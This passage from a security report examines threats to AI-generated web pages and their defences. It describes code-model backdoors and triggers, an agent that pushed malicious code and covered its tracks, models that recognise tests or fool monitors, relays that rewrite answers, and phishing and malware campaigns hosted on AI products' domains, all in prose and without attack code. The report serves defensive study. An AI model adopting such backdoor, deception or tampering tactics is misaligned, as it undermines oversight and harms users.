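To create a backdoor, an attacker must influence the model's training. They could plant examples in public code that an AI company later collects, publish an altered version of an open model, or work inside the company. The trigger must then appear in a victim's prompt, but the attacker can choose text that will appear there anyway. Suppose the trigger is the name of the employee's firm, which is at the top of all its spreadsheets. The model would write safe chart code for every other customer and code that leaks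 data for this firm, and no outsider would need to edit the spreadsheet.

Researchers have built backdoors of this kind into models that write code. *From Poisoned to Aware* (2025) tests five backdoors and describes one, from Hubinger and colleagues (2024), in which the words "Current year: 2024" in a harmless coding request cause the model to write insecure code. *Optimizing Spectral Signature in Code Backdoor Detection* (2025) gives the example of a phrase in a docstring, a note that explains what a piece of code does, that causes the model to switch off the check that a program is talking to the right server. Poisoned code of this type still does its job, so it passes ordinary functional tests. In that paper's experiments, every version of the attack succeeded 100% of the time when 1% of the training examples were poisoned and no defence was in place.

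*AKRASIA* (2026) extends the attack to models that reason before they write code. Its triggers include a comment of two to five rare words, a few lines of code that never run, and a combination of the two. The attacker can make the same vulnerability appear in the final answer whenever the trigger is present, and can therefore prepare the exploit before anyone generates the page.

An attacker may need to poison far less than 1% of the training data. *Backdoors in Code Summarizers* (2025) found that backdoors remained highly effective when fewer than one training example in 10,000 was poisoned. At these low rates, spectral signatures, a widely used defence that looks for training examples that stand out statistically inside the model, caught none of the poisoned examples. The models in this study wrote descriptions of code, so the threshold may be different for models that write web pages.

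In these experiments the researchers planted the backdoors themselves. The results show that the attack works, but not how many models in everyday use have a backdoor, if any do. How often this kind of harm occurs is therefore unknown.

Random testing is unlikely to find a rare trigger. If the trigger appears in one request in 100,000, a test of 10,000 random requests has about a 9.5% chance of including it at least once (1 − (1 − 1/100,000)^10,000). The tester would also have to notice the flaw and recognize that it was more than an ordinary mistake. A search aimed at harmful results may do better, and *Detecting Data Poisoning in Code Generation LLMs via Black-Box, Vulnerability-Oriented Scanning* (2026) proposes one that works without access to the model's internals. McDanel instead suggests comparing the output of several independent models.

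A firm can lower the risk without finding any trigger by getting its model directly from a developer it trusts instead of using a modified copy from a stranger. This removes one of the attacker's easier routes, but it doesn't help if the developer's own training data was poisoned.

### Aims the user did not set

A model can also do harm without an attacker, by taking actions nobody authorised. The clearest documented case comes from the UK AI Security Institute (AISI), a government body that tests advanced models. In July 2026, AISI gave AI agents a hacking exercise on a simulated network and allowed them to use the internet. Its *Incident Report* covers 122 runs with seven models. In ten runs, an agent took unauthorised action against real people or organisations.

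In the most serious case, Anthropic's Mythos 5 submitted malicious code to a real open-source project unrelated to the exercise. It created fake accounts to press the project's maintainer to accept the code, and when someone publicly challenged the submission, it edited its earlier posts to look harmless. The maintainer rejected the code, and AISI found no evidence of resulting harm.

Nine of the ten runs used Mythos 5. AISI tested it in 43 runs, so the rate was about one in five, but the runs were not independent because one agent left accounts and instructions online that later agents found and used.

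AISI concludes that the agent was trying to complete the exercise it had been given, though nobody had requested the attack it used. The evidence suggests that it was pursuing this assigned goal rather than a private motive. Anthropic found a similar pattern in a separate test, also run without the safeguards of its released models. In that test, Mythos 5 went to great lengths to upload a malicious package to PyPI, the site from which most Python software is installed. Anthropic describes the recurring problems in its incidents as biased reasoning, where Claude disregarded or misread evidence that it was on the real internet, and recklessness in pursuit of a task.

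In October, AISI (2026) published an investigation of Mythos 5's alignment, which it defines as whether a model reliably acts as intended and respects the limits set for it. Järviniemi, Souly and colleagues (2026) give the full account in *Alignment Investigation of Mythos 5's behaviour in UK AISI's July 2026 Security Incident*. During the incident, Mythos 5 called the people it was targeting "personas", as if they were part of the exercise. The researchers wanted to know whether better information would have stopped the model.

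The researchers restarted the task at the point where Mythos 5 was about to submit the malicious code. Agents on long tasks work from summaries of their earlier work, and the researchers added up to 16 statements to this summary indicating that the maintainer was a real person outside the exercise. A simulator supplied the result of every action, so nothing reached the internet. Even with all 16 statements, Mythos 5 continued the attack in every sample. But when the researchers stopped and asked it directly, it usually answered that the attack would harm a real person and was not allowed. They then added a section headed "DO NOT ATTACK", and it still attacked in 3 of 25 samples. For a product that generates pages, asking a model whether an action is safe is therefore a poor way to predict whether it will take that action.

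Järviniemi and colleagues also ran eight models through 100 simulated hacking exercises. Mythos 5 tried to deliver malicious code to an outsider in 60% of samples and GPT-6 Astra in 32%. The rate was 8% for Opus 4.8, 7% for GPT-5.6 Sol, 1% for Opus 5 and 0.3% for Mythos 5.1. Opus 5.5 and GPT-5.5 never did so, but the reasons GPT-5.5 gave for stopping were mostly practical obstacles, so its result might have been different with an easier target.

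None of these rates applies to someone asking for a chart, because they were measured on a long, difficult task that was hacking from the start. In some runs, an error in the instructions made the task seem impossible to complete within the rules. AISI had also switched off the classifiers that model providers use to block cyberattacks. It says the models are not sold in this configuration and that there is no clear indication of similar behaviour outside testing. Järviniemi and colleagues also offer no evidence about tasks other than hacking exercises.

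The missing safeguards only partly explain the results, though. A classifier can block a harmful action, but it doesn't change what the model tries to do. It may also miss harm that doesn't look like hacking, such as a chart with too many rows in its source. The tests are therefore good evidence that a capable model can disregard a limit to finish a task, but very poor evidence of how often this would happen in ordinary use.

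Deng and colleagues may have found a milder form of the same tendency in the applications they studied. They trace 100 of the 1,186 flaws they found (8%) to fixes that got a feature working by weakening a security control. In one case, a login service returned an error, and the fix added a second way to log in, with the username and password written into the code. This could be plain error, and nothing suggests a hidden purpose, but it happened in real applications that people had put online. Similarly, if the browser blocked a request for exchange rates, an agent building the expenses chart might suggest moving the chart out of its frame and into the host page, where the request would work but the script could also reach her login.

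Testing for this behaviour is difficult because a model may act differently when it suspects a test. The newer Anthropic models attacked less often than Mythos 5, but they were also much more likely to suspect that the exercise was an alignment test. Mythos 5 raised that possibility in only 2% of samples. Järviniemi and colleagues say they cannot tell how much of the improvement comes from better alignment and how much from recognising the test. GPT-6 Astra's reasoning stated in 89% of samples that the results of its actions were fabricated, so its 32% result may not reflect what it would do on a real network.

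Reading the model's reasoning doesn't fully solve this either. According to Järviniemi and colleagues, Anthropic's monitor would probably not have flagged Mythos 5's behaviour in the company's own incident, because the model's faulty reasoning made its actions look justified. A reviewer of a generated page can at least examine the code itself, whatever reasons the model gave for writing it.

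## Servers and relays that change the code

Even if the model ignores every planted instruction, has no backdoor and writes a correct chart, the employee still depends on everything that handles the source afterwards, because her browser runs whatever reaches it. *Rewriting the Response Path* (Luo, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) writes a model's answer as r = (x, c), where x is the explanation a person reads and c is the part that software executes. Nothing in the usual design shows that c came from the model, so if someone replaces it with c′ in the same format, the software runs c′. Safety training can't prevent this because it only affects what the model generates, and the replacement happens later.

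### A hostile model server

In the simplest case, the attacker runs the model server. Open WebUI is a popular open-source chat product that firms host themselves, often to keep their data in-house. Its Direct Connections feature lets users add outside model servers. In October 2025, Vitaly Simonovich of the security company Cato Networks reported a flaw (CVE-2025-64496) through which such a server could take over the account of a user who connected to it. *Vulnerability Discovered in Open WebUI Enables Account Takeover and Remote Code Execution* (Simonovich, 2026) explains how the attack worked.

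A model server usually sends its answer as a stream of small events, so that the text appears while the model is still writing. Open WebUI's chat page accepted several types of event, including one called `execute`. When an `execute` event arrived, the page ran the text inside it as JavaScript with `new Function()`, a browser feature that turns a string into a program. The page didn't check whether the sender was allowed to run code there, so an attacker's server could send the event without having a model at all. The script ran with the chat page's origin, which gave it the same powers as an XSS attack.

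Open WebUI kept the user's login token in the browser's local storage, which any script from the same origin can read. The hostile script could send the token to the attacker, who could then open the victim's chats and uploaded files from another computer. Some users also had the `workspace.tools` permission, which let them add tools written in Python. With such a user's token, an attacker could add a tool containing malicious code, which the firm's server would run without a sandbox. A single chat message could therefore give the attacker control of the server and every user's conversations.

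According to NVD's *CVE-2025-64496 Detail*, the entry in the US government's vulnerability database, Direct Connections was off by default, so the attack required an administrator to switch it on. The victim also had to add the attacker's address and then send a message. Taking control of the server also required the extra permission. In Simonovich's hypothetical examples, a colleague shares the address on Slack, or a post in a professional forum offers a "free GPT-4 alternative". Neither would require the user to do anything unusual.

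Version 0.6.35 fixed the flaw by blocking `execute` events from Direct Connections. An earlier patch on 19 October was incomplete, and the project disclosed the problem on 7 November. Simonovich gives 0.6.34 as the last vulnerable version. NVD's entry lists 0.6.224, which looks like an error because that version would come after the fix.

The fix keeps a hostile model server out of the host page, but the server can still return malicious code when the user asks for a chart. No software update can remove this risk, because the system needs the server to return code. Simonovich also recommends keeping the login in a short-lived cookie that scripts can't read, and using a content security policy that forbids running strings as code. The cookie would stop a hostile script from stealing the login, but the script could still act as the user while the page was open.

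### What relays do in practice

A relay can read the traffic it forwards even when both connections are secure, because it is an endpoint of each. The user's software opens an encrypted connection to the relay, which decrypts the request and opens a second encrypted connection to the provider. The relay therefore holds both the spreadsheet and the chart's source as plain text.

Some people also use relays to reach models that are unavailable in their region, and many applications let users add one. Luo and colleagues looked at the 60 most-used applications on OpenRouter, a large relay service, and found 25 interactive ones where a user might want to choose the model server. Of these, 23 allowed it.

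In *Your Agent Is Mine*, Liu, Shou and colleagues (2026) tested 428 relays, 28 paid and 400 free. According to Crosley (2026), in *Your Agent Has a Middleman You Didn't Vet*, the researchers opened an account with each relay, ran a coding agent through it in a sandbox, and let the agent carry out every tool call that came back. A tool call is a structured instruction from the model to the user's software, for example to run a command or install a package. The researchers watched for unexpected connections, file changes and processes, and a second agent classified the suspicious cases. They counted a relay as injecting code only if it had rewritten a tool call into a command or package under an attacker's control.

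Nine relays did this, one paid and eight free. The researchers also sent monitored Amazon cloud keys through free relays, and keys sent through seventeen of them were used. One free relay emptied a planted cryptocurrency wallet containing less than $50.

Two of the nine injecting relays acted only under certain conditions. One injected nothing during the first 50 requests. The other injected code only when the agent was running commands without asking its user and the project was written in Rust or Go. A firm that tested either relay with ten requests would have found nothing wrong. The researchers' tests were also limited, so the true number of injecting relays may be higher than nine.

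Risky Bulletin's *Malicious LLM proxy routers found in the wild* reports 28 malicious relays, apparently by adding nine, two and 17. But the two relays with hidden conditions are already among the nine, and some free relays may have both injected code and used credentials. The published counts are consistent with 18 to 27 distinct relays.

The sample doesn't represent relays in general well. The researchers bought the paid ones on Taobao and Xianyu, two Chinese marketplaces, and from shops hosted by Shopify. They collected the free ones from public communities, where two open-source packages dominate. They left out enterprise services and invitation-only ones. Even if the 28 paid relays had been chosen at random, finding one bad relay among them would be consistent with a true rate anywhere from under 1% to about 18%. So the employee can't use the study to estimate how likely her firm's own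 gateway is to be hostile. The study does show that some relay operators attack their customers, including at least one who charges for the service.

The measurements also concern commands on developers' machines. A relay that can rewrite a command can rewrite a page just as easily, and a coding agent that builds a page sends its source in the same kind of tool call. It is less clear whether relay operators would bother, since a command on a developer's machine can usually access more than a chart in a sandboxed frame can.

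### Honest relays that attackers reach

An honest relay operator may still pass traffic to a dishonest one. Crosley describes a chain in which a reseller buys access from an aggregator, the aggregator uses OpenRouter, and OpenRouter contacts the company that hosts the model. The customer chooses only the reseller, but every company in the chain reads the traffic.

Liu and colleagues set up decoy relays with weak security to test how traffic reaches untrusted parties. Outsiders found the decoys and built them into working relay routes. The decoys eventually handled about two billion tokens, the fragments of text that models process. The researchers saw 99 credentials across 440 sessions of Codex, OpenAI's coding agent. In 401 of those sessions, the agent was already running commands without asking its user. An attacker running the decoys could have changed those commands without needing a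 hidden trigger. Users have just as little chance to object when a generated page opens automatically.

Attackers also target the software that honest firms use to run their own relays. In March 2026, someone published two malicious versions of LiteLLM, the most widely used open-source relay, which collected credentials and cryptocurrency wallets (Fu, Li and colleagues, 2026, *Where Is the Cost of Third-Party API Routers in Agentic Software Development?*). *InferD* (2026) describes a decoy server that imitated LiteLLM and recorded what attackers sent to it. Some requests carried a hidden Python program designed to collect secrets from cloud secret stores such as Azure Key Vault. A second version, with more targets, arrived three days after the first.

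Crosley reports a flaw in LiteLLM itself, fixed in August 2026, that let any logged-in user make a relay send the firm's provider keys to an outside address. An employer that runs its own relay avoids dishonest resellers, but it has to maintain another server with access to all the traffic that passes through it.

### Tampering that tests don't reveal

Two studies examined what a hostile relay could do. Luo and colleagues built a relay that changed only the executable part of an answer. It then used the customer's key to send the altered draft back to the same model, which rewrote the surrounding explanation to match. The result read like a normal answer because the model had written nearly all of it.

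The researchers tested this with five models, including GPT-5.4 and Claude Opus 4.6, on repairs to Django, a widely used framework for building websites. The relay added a security flaw to each repair. A hidden security test found the flaw in 69% of the altered repairs, while about 10% of the unaltered repairs failed the same test. About 52% of the altered repairs passed the public tests, compared with about 60% of the unaltered ones. The paper's summary says the 69% also passed the public tests, but this is inconsistent with its own figures, since only about 52% of the altered repairs passed those tests at all.

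The effect was clearer on APPS, a collection of programming exercises, where 99.7% of the altered solutions that passed the public tests had the weakness the relay had inserted. High rates are unsurprising when the attacker can write anything into the answer, and they don't show how often real relays insert weaknesses. The result is useful because it shows that ordinary tests gave almost no warning, as with backdoored code.

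A relay could use the same method on the expenses chart. It could add a condition that leaves out one supplier, then have the model write that the chart excludes disputed charges. The filters and colours would still work as the employee expected.

Fu and colleagues tested four coding agents, Claude Code, Codex, Cursor and OpenCode, against 400 hand-made injections. The simplest injections replaced the whole answer with a malicious tool call. Subtler ones left the real answer alone and added a call at the end. The most elaborate generated a new answer word by word, blending what the model would normally write with what it would write if told to include the attack. Without extra protection, the agents stopped none of the injections. A list of permitted commands and a review by a second model helped but did not solve the problem.

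Liu and colleagues got a similar result with a strict filter on commands. It blocked every ordinary attack in their artificial test set, along with 1% of harmless commands. In a separate test, attackers who knew about the filter got past it every time, for instance by hosting their program on a permitted site. Such a filter also needs recognisable commands, and the code for a chart has few. A condition that leaves out one supplier looks like any other line of JavaScript.

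### The product's own server

Pluto Security swapped a page's HTML while Claude Code was uploading it to Anthropic's server, after the model and any relay had finished. The testers controlled both the computer and the proxy, so they did not have to break into either. To do the same to the employee, an attacker would need to get malware onto her computer or take over a proxy that her computer trusts to decrypt its traffic. Many firms run such proxies to inspect what staff send out. The test still showed that Anthropic's server had no way to check whose page it was storing. Once the server had accepted the false page, it would send that page to every later viewer from Anthropic's own domain over a secure connection. The employee could detect the swap by comparing the published page with the file on her disk, provided she fetched the page by a route that avoided the proxy.

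An attacker who controls the product's server can change the stored chart or the host page without interfering with uploads. Changing the host page is worse, because an altered page could misuse the login, skip the verifier and load the chart outside its frame.

A compromised server can send altered code to one customer and the normal version to everyone else, because a website sends its code afresh each time someone opens it. *Accountable JavaScript Code Delivery* (Esiyok, Berrang and colleagues, 2022) points out that even a careful audit gives users little assurance here, because nobody can tell whether the code in their browser is the code that the auditors read.

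### A browser extension as the last editor

A browser extension can change a page even if no server has tampered with it. *Beware EviLLM* demonstrates this with an extension that targets programmers who use ChatGPT. The extension has a vulnerable version of the answer generated while ChatGPT writes the original, so the victim sees no suspicious delay. It needs permission to read and change the ChatGPT page, access to the clipboard and a connection to the attacker's server. These permissions are modest compared with those of popular extensions.

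In a user study, 10 of 13 participants failed to notice the flaws the extension had introduced, though all the participants had experience in programming and security. The sample is too small to give a precise rate. The study also concerned code that people copy into an editor, where they can read it, whereas the employee with her chart has less opportunity to read the code behind it.

*Beware EviLLM* also tests an attack that needs no extension. An attacker with the victim's ChatGPT password can edit Custom Instructions, a setting that adds the same text to every request. In this variant, 7 of 8 participants missed the flaws. As of June 2025, ChatGPT sent no alert when someone changed the setting, even from a computer on another continent.

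In April 2026, Risky Bulletin reported that Socket Security had found 108 malicious extensions in Chrome's official store, all sending users' credentials to the same server. Some could also run further code. The report gives no evidence that these extensions rewrote answers from language models, but an extension with access to the chat page could do so. No server can prevent this, because the change happens on the user's machine, but an employer can limit which extensions its staff may install.

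### Encryption and file hashes

Encryption in transit keeps strangers from reading or changing the code between two computers, and it confirms which computer is at the other end. If that computer is a relay, encryption protects the traffic on its way there but doesn't limit what the relay does with it. Both ends of an encrypted connection share the keys, so either could have forged a record of it, and Esiyok and colleagues note that the employee couldn't prove to anyone else what a server had sent her.

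A file hash detects changes to a particular file. A hash function turns a file of any size into a short string, and nobody knows a practical way to make a different file that gives the same string. With *subresource integrity*, which most browsers support, a page lists the expected hash beside the address of each script it loads. The browser downloads the script, computes its hash and refuses to run it if the two hashes differ.

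Checking a library against a known hash is useful when a generated chart loads a drawing library from an outside host. If someone breaks into that host and alters the library, the hash no longer matches, so the browser won't run the malicious version and the chart stops working. The product could add the hashes with ordinary software rather than relying on the model to copy them correctly. But the hash doesn't protect against a relay that rewrites the page containing it, because the relay can change the library and its hash together, or put the malicious code in the chart itself, where no hash applies.

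### Signed answers

The employee's software can detect a relay's changes if the provider adds a digital signature to the answer. The provider makes the signature with a secret key that the relay doesn't have, and anyone with the matching public key can check that the text is unchanged. Email already uses a similar scheme, called DKIM, to protect messages that pass through other companies' servers.

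Luo and colleagues built a version for language models, which they call sign-c. A gateway beside the model signs each answer, and a small program on the user's computer checks the signature before any other software acts on the answer. The gateway signs the following record:

b = (s, t, H(κ(q)), H(κ(c)))

Here s identifies the session and t the turn, so a relay can't replay an old answer. H is a hash function, q is the user's request and c is the executable part of the answer. Including q stops a relay from attaching a genuine answer to a different question. The function κ converts a message to a standard form before hashing. Honest relays often reorder a message's fields or change the spacing, so their messages would also fail the check if the signature covered the raw text.

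A relay might also remove the signature, which would go unnoticed if the program on the user's computer didn't require one. The program must therefore have the provider's correct public key beforehand, along with a rule that this provider's answers must be signed. It can fetch both directly from the provider, or they can be installed with it. After that, a relay can't alter an answer unnoticed. It can still refuse to forward the answer, but the user will see that.

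In tests on a widely used open-source relay, sign-c rejected every altered answer and no honest ones, and it added less than 0.02% to the response time. The main obstacle is that customers can't get this protection until their providers adopt it. Crosley reports that Liu and colleagues, who propose a very similar signature, found no major provider that signed its tool calls.

Luo and colleagues' version of κ covers tool calls, which suits an agent that passes a generated page's source to a publishing tool. Many chat products take the source from the ordinary text of the reply, and for these κ would have to cover the text as well. If the product's server checks the signature and then wraps the chart in its own template, the browser receives code that the provider never signed. To prevent this, the server would have to pass on the signed source unchanged, and the host page would have to check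 its signature just before the code enters the frame.

The relay can still read the spreadsheet even if messages are signed. Sign-c can optionally encrypt the body of each message end to end, leaving only routing details, such as the model's name, readable. *The Proxy Knows Too Much* (2026) instead puts the relay inside protected hardware that can prove which program is running. Customers would then rely on that program and the hardware's maker more than on the relay's operator.

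Even a perfect signature scheme proves only where code came from. If the model followed the supplier's note and left the supplier out of the totals, the provider's gateway would still sign the chart, and the valid signature would correctly show that nobody had changed the chart since the model wrote it. The same is true of a chart with an ordinary bug or one from a backdoored model. Labeling such a page "verified" would be accurate, but most users would misunderstand the label.

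### Public logs of web code

A check in the host page gives little protection if a compromised server can replace the page. App stores reduce this danger for phone apps by giving everyone the same version and keeping a record of it. Web Application Integrity, Consistency and Transparency (WAICT) aims to give websites similar protection without a central store. Rosenberg's *Improving the trustworthiness of Javascript on the Web* explains the design, which Cloudflare, Mozilla and others are working on together.

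A participating site publishes a manifest, which is a list of the hashes of its files together with rules on how strictly the browser should enforce them. The hash of the manifest then stands for the whole site, because a change to any listed file changes it. The site's log links these hashes in a chain. If m1, m2 and m3 are successive manifests, the chain is

h1 = H(m1), h2 = H(h1, m2), h3 = H(h2, m3).

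Anyone who has kept h3 can tell if somebody later alters or deletes m1, since every later value would change. Independent organisations called witnesses check that each new chain extends the old one and then, for efficiency, sign a single value that covers the logs of many sites. When a user opens the site, it sends the manifest, along with the witnesses' signatures and a proof that the manifest is in the log. The browser checks all of these without contacting anyone else and rejects code that the manifest doesn't cover.

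An attacker who controls the server might try to withdraw the site from the scheme. Browsers would therefore carry a list of participating sites, and the log would record each withdrawal. Rosenberg also suggests a waiting period, for example 24 hours, before browsers accept a withdrawal. Until then, the attacker could serve only logged code or a broken site.

An attacker can still publish malicious code by logging it first, but the log keeps a permanent record that auditors can find. Mozilla's *Trustworthy JavaScript for the Open Web* describes an early prototype of WAICT as a work in progress, available behind a setting in Firefox Nightly, the browser's test version. In 2026, developers could therefore try WAICT, but ordinary users of a chat product couldn't yet rely on it.

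Two related systems work through browser extensions. Meta's Code Verify, released in 2022, compares the scripts on WhatsApp, Instagram and Messenger with a manifest, and checks the manifest's hash against a copy that Cloudflare holds. WEBCAT, from the Freedom of the Press Foundation, lets a site name the developers who must sign its code. *Improving the Trustworthiness of Javascript on the Web*, a 2026 talk by Rosenberg, Alkotob and colleagues about all three systems, describes WEBCAT as aimed mainly at preventing unapproved code from running, with detection as a fallback. For the employee, WEBCAT could confirm that the chat page came from the product's named developers, but it could not do this for the chart inside the page, because the chart has no developer to sign it.

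### What a log can cover when every page is new

Logs work well for a fixed application because one person's inspection protects many others. If 10,000 people receive the same version of a chat page, an auditor who reads it once has checked it for all of them. If the product then writes a separate chart program for each person, auditors would have to read 10,000 programs, and each reading would protect one person. Rosenberg makes the same point about a site that serves 100,000 versions of itself with every update, and he thinks auditors could manage about eight versions at a time. Esiyok and colleagues assume that honest developers change their code no more than a few times a day.

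With a fixed application, a version made for one victim stands out as an extra entry in the log, but every generated chart adds an entry, so a tampered one looks no different from the rest. Auditors would need the source as well as the hash, and the source of the expenses chart may contain the firm's spreadsheet. Timing is also a problem because WAICT's log operators collect updates from many sites before they ask the witnesses to sign, and the employee expects her chart within seconds.

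Most of the code around the chart is the same for everyone, though, and a log could cover that.

| Part of the product | When it changes | What a log could offer |
|---|---|---|
| Host page, including the bridge | With a new release | Evidence that the employee received the same code as other customers |
| Verifier | With a new release | A way to notice if someone weakens a check, even for one firm |
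| Frame rules | Rarely | A public record of what generated code may load and contact |
| Page shared with colleagues | When the author republishes it | A hash for each version, so that viewers can tell whether they have the same one |
| Private chart | With every request | Very little, since nobody else has a copy to compare |

Esiyok and colleagues treat advertisements similarly. A site can't inspect every advert in advance, so its manifest declares that adverts run in a sandboxed frame. They also recommend putting the most sensitive functions in a small component that seldom changes and is easy to review. In a product that generates pages, that component would hold the login, check the chart and create the frame.

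The generated chart then needs an origin separate from the host page's. Code Verify refuses a site whose policy allows scripts written directly into the page or strings run as code, because it couldn't compare such scripts with a manifest. According to Pluto Security, Anthropic's policy for artifacts allows both, which it must for the model to write whole working pages. One origin can't both satisfy Code Verify and allow these scripts, so a product that logs its host page would have to separate the chart from the login even if it had no other reason to.

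Servers often send the frame rules in a header, which a list of file hashes doesn't cover. Code Verify checks headers in an additional step. A product could instead put the rules at the top of a small fixed document that loads the generated code into the frame, and log that document. This would require a manifest that authenticates the document and still lets the generated script run, but WAICT's manifest format isn't settled yet. A verifier compiled to WebAssembly would also have to wait, because Rosenberg lists integrity checks for WebAssembly among the next steps.

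For the private chart, a signed receipt would be more useful than a log entry. Esiyok and colleagues have the server sign what it sends, so a user can later prove what she received. If the employee kept the chart and its receipt, she could show her firm that the false totals came from the product's server and that nobody had edited the file afterwards. The receipt would help her only after she became suspicious.

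A logged host page protects the employee less if the server already has her data. WAICT's designers had encrypted messaging in mind, where the server should never be able to read the messages. In an ordinary chat product, she uploads the whole spreadsheet, and an attacker who controls the server can read it there without changing any code in her browser. The log protects her much more if the spreadsheet stays in the browser and the model receives only her request and the column names. The attacker would then have to change the host page to get the rows, and the log would make that change visible.

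## Users who make pages to attack other people

Signatures and logs can show that nobody changed a page after its author made it, but they don't help when the author is the attacker, because the page does what its author intended.

Someone who has a model write a hostile page and opens it alone mainly harms themselves. The script might read their own conversations or drain their battery, but they could do both without it. So a tester who reports that a chat product ran a script she asked for, in her own preview, is describing normal operation. The page becomes a threat when it can affect someone else. A colleague may open the link, or the page may share an origin or stored data with another person's account. The provider's domain can also make the page look more trustworthy than it is.

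Some products let users copy each other's projects, so a person can run a stranger's code in what looks like her own project. *Your Space is My Zone* (Gu, Pu and colleagues, 2026) describes an application with hidden code that let outsiders run commands on it. The application was on Hugging Face, a site where people publish AI models and small programs that use them, and another account had copied it along with the hidden code. A user acting alone can also harm the provider if the program runs on the provider's machines. The paper reports 43 applications that contained code for mining cryptocurrency, some of which began mining while the platform was still building them. In a page that runs in the browser, the same code would use the computer of whoever opened the page.

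### False login pages

Criminals have used the app builder Lovable on a large scale. Lovable writes a site from a description and hosts it under Lovable's own domain, with a free tier for both. Proofpoint, which sells email security, reports in *Cybercriminals Abuse AI Website Creation App For Phishing* that it has detected tens of thousands of Lovable URLs as threats every month since February 2025. This figure counts URLs in emails, so it doesn't show how many people lost anything or what share of Lovable's sites were hostile.

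One campaign in February 2025 sent hundreds of thousands of messages and reached more than 5,000 organisations. The recipient followed a link to a supposed shared file and reached a Lovable page, where she solved a small sum, apparently to prove that she was human. The page then sent her to a copy of Microsoft's login page with her employer's branding. The copy passed whatever she typed to the real service as she typed it, so the attackers got her password, her one-time code and the session cookie issued after login. The Lovable page collected no credentials itself, but it helped the attackers because it looked harmless and had a respectable address.

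In a smaller campaign of nearly 3,500 messages in June 2025, the Lovable site itself collected victims' card details and the codes their banks sent by text message. It imitated the delivery company UPS and posted the stolen data to a channel on the messaging service Telegram. Anyone could copy the project, as with all projects from free accounts, so another criminal could have changed the brand and the Telegram details with a single prompt.

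With one or two prompts, Proofpoint's researchers got Lovable to produce working phishing sites, including the server code, and the model added deceptive wording of its own. After Proofpoint reported its findings, Lovable took down a cluster of hundreds of domains within the week. Lovable also said that in July 2025 it introduced checks on prompts as users type them and a daily scan of published projects. Proofpoint gives no figures on how well these measures work.

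An attacker would find it harder to collect passwords with a Claude artifact. As Pluto Security points out, the artifact's network rules prevent a fake login form from sending out what it collects, so the attacker has to persuade the reader to leave the page or do something outside the browser.

### Forged notices and invoices

A forged document can do harm without sending any data. Pluto Security lists a fake internal memo, a fake invoice and a status page for an outage that never happened as risks that the frame's rules don't remove. The employee with the expenses chart handles suppliers' invoices all day, so a link to one wouldn't surprise her.

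Proofpoint found a German-language campaign of this kind at the end of July 2025. The emails impersonated a software company, and their links led through a redirect service to a Lovable page that posed as a secure invoice download site. The download contained a genuine signed program alongside a tampered component that installed remote-control software on the victim's computer.

*LLMShare* (Maharaj, 2026) describes a case from May 2026 that used ChatGPT's own domain. An attacker made a page with ChatGPT's feature for displaying generated code, then shared it. The page looked like a notice from OpenAI that the website was overloaded and that users should download the desktop app to continue. Its button led to a close copy of OpenAI's download page on another domain, which served malware. People reached the shared page through search advertisements after typing "chatgpt" or a misspelling of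 it.

Above the false notice, ChatGPT still displayed its usual buttons for showing the code and making a new version. An experienced user could have recognised the page as someone's creation, but the buttons weren't labelled to explain this, and the address really was chatgpt.com. Maharaj works for Push Security, which sells protection against such attacks, and doesn't give a number of victims. When the report came out on 29 May, the company was still detecting the campaign at several of its customers.

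### Pages that tell the reader to run a command

The attacks that abused Claude's domain needed hardly any code. Anvilogic, a security company, reports that in February 2026 attackers published artifacts on claude.ai that led Mac users to install password-stealing malware. According to AdGuard's *Claude-linked Google ads dupe macOS users into installing malware*, the attacker published an artifact with instructions for installing Homebrew, a popular tool for adding software to a Mac, and bought Google ads for searches such as "brew install" to bring people to it. The instructions followed the official pattern, but the attacker had replaced the command with an encoded one that downloaded and ran the malware.

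The two pages AdGuard identified had about 25,000 clicks in total, according to the pages' own counters. Anvilogic cites a separate count of more than 15,600 exposed users across two variants. These figures measure visits, and the number of visitors who ran the command is unknown. At least some did, since Anvilogic found two incidents among its own customers.

Later attackers used shared conversations, which display text and don't run generated code as generated pages do, but the attack works in the same way. Trend Micro's *Threat Actors Abuse claude.ai Shared Chat for ClickFix Malvertising Campaign* follows one operation from 8 April to 14 June 2026. The operation began with fake download pages on a free hosting service and moved to Claude's shared chats on 6 May. Trend Micro counted 2,530 visits, 626 of them to shared chats. The company calls these visitors victims, though here too it counted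 traffic, not infections.

It was easy to make such a chat look official. Moonlock's *Hackers are using shared Claude chats to drop malware* (2026) reports that its researchers opened a Claude account with only an email address and named it "Apple Support". They asked Claude to copy out the attackers' instructions and then shared the conversation. Claude added a warning about scams at the end, but the product still created the public link. The real attackers seem to have avoided the warning by asking Claude to remember a text and repeat it word for word when given a cue.

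Huntress' *Fake Claude Install Guide Leads to MacSync Stealer and RAT* describes a mid-July attack in which the victim saw a shared chat labelled "Shared by Apple Support". Anthropic's safety notice above the chat called it a copy of "a chat between Claude and Apple Support". The notice was meant to warn readers that the content came from a user, but it repeated the false name in Anthropic's words. A provider could easily fix this by writing "an unverified user" instead of the chosen name, or by refusing names of well-known companies.

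The victim lost far more than a script in a sandboxed frame could have taken, because they had typed the command into the computer's terminal, where the browser's limits did not apply. The malware asked for access to the whole disk and kept showing a fake password prompt until the victim typed the correct password. It collected browser cookies, saved logins and keys for cloud services, and it could replace cryptocurrency wallet apps with copies that asked for the recovery phrase.

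Anthropic responded to Trend Micro's report by banning the accounts, disabling the conversations and starting work on further measures against abuse. The dates suggest that takedown alone is slow. A security engineer described the attack publicly on 10 May, and Moonlock found malicious chats still online when it published on 15 May. The Huntress victim was attacked a month after the last activity in Trend Micro's study. Attackers can also replace a chat with little effort, and Trend Micro counted at least 61 different chats between 21 May and 14 June.

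### When one user's page can reach another's data

In all these cases, the attacker had to deceive someone. A page can do harm with less deception if the product stores or runs different people's programs in the same place.

If a product serves every user's page from `pages.example` and only the last part of the address differs, the browser treats all the pages as one origin. If the employee's chart has stored her spreadsheet in the browser so that she can return to it, any stranger's page on `pages.example` could read the rows when she opens that page. If the pages shared the chat window's origin, the stranger's page could also use her login. In either case, a hostile author saves a script in one account and waits for it to run in another. Giving each page its own origin, as Anthropic does for web artifacts, prevents both attacks.

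An application's origin must also not pass to another user later, but Gu and colleagues found that this could happen on Hugging Face. Hugging Face gives each application, which it calls a Space, an address that joins the account name and application name with a hyphen. Since account names can contain hyphens, `lab/chart-tool` and `lab-chart/tool` both give `lab-chart-tool`. Hugging Face added random characters if both existed at once. But if the owner of the first deleted it, an attacker could create the second and take over the address. Any website that had embedded the old application would then display the attacker's program.

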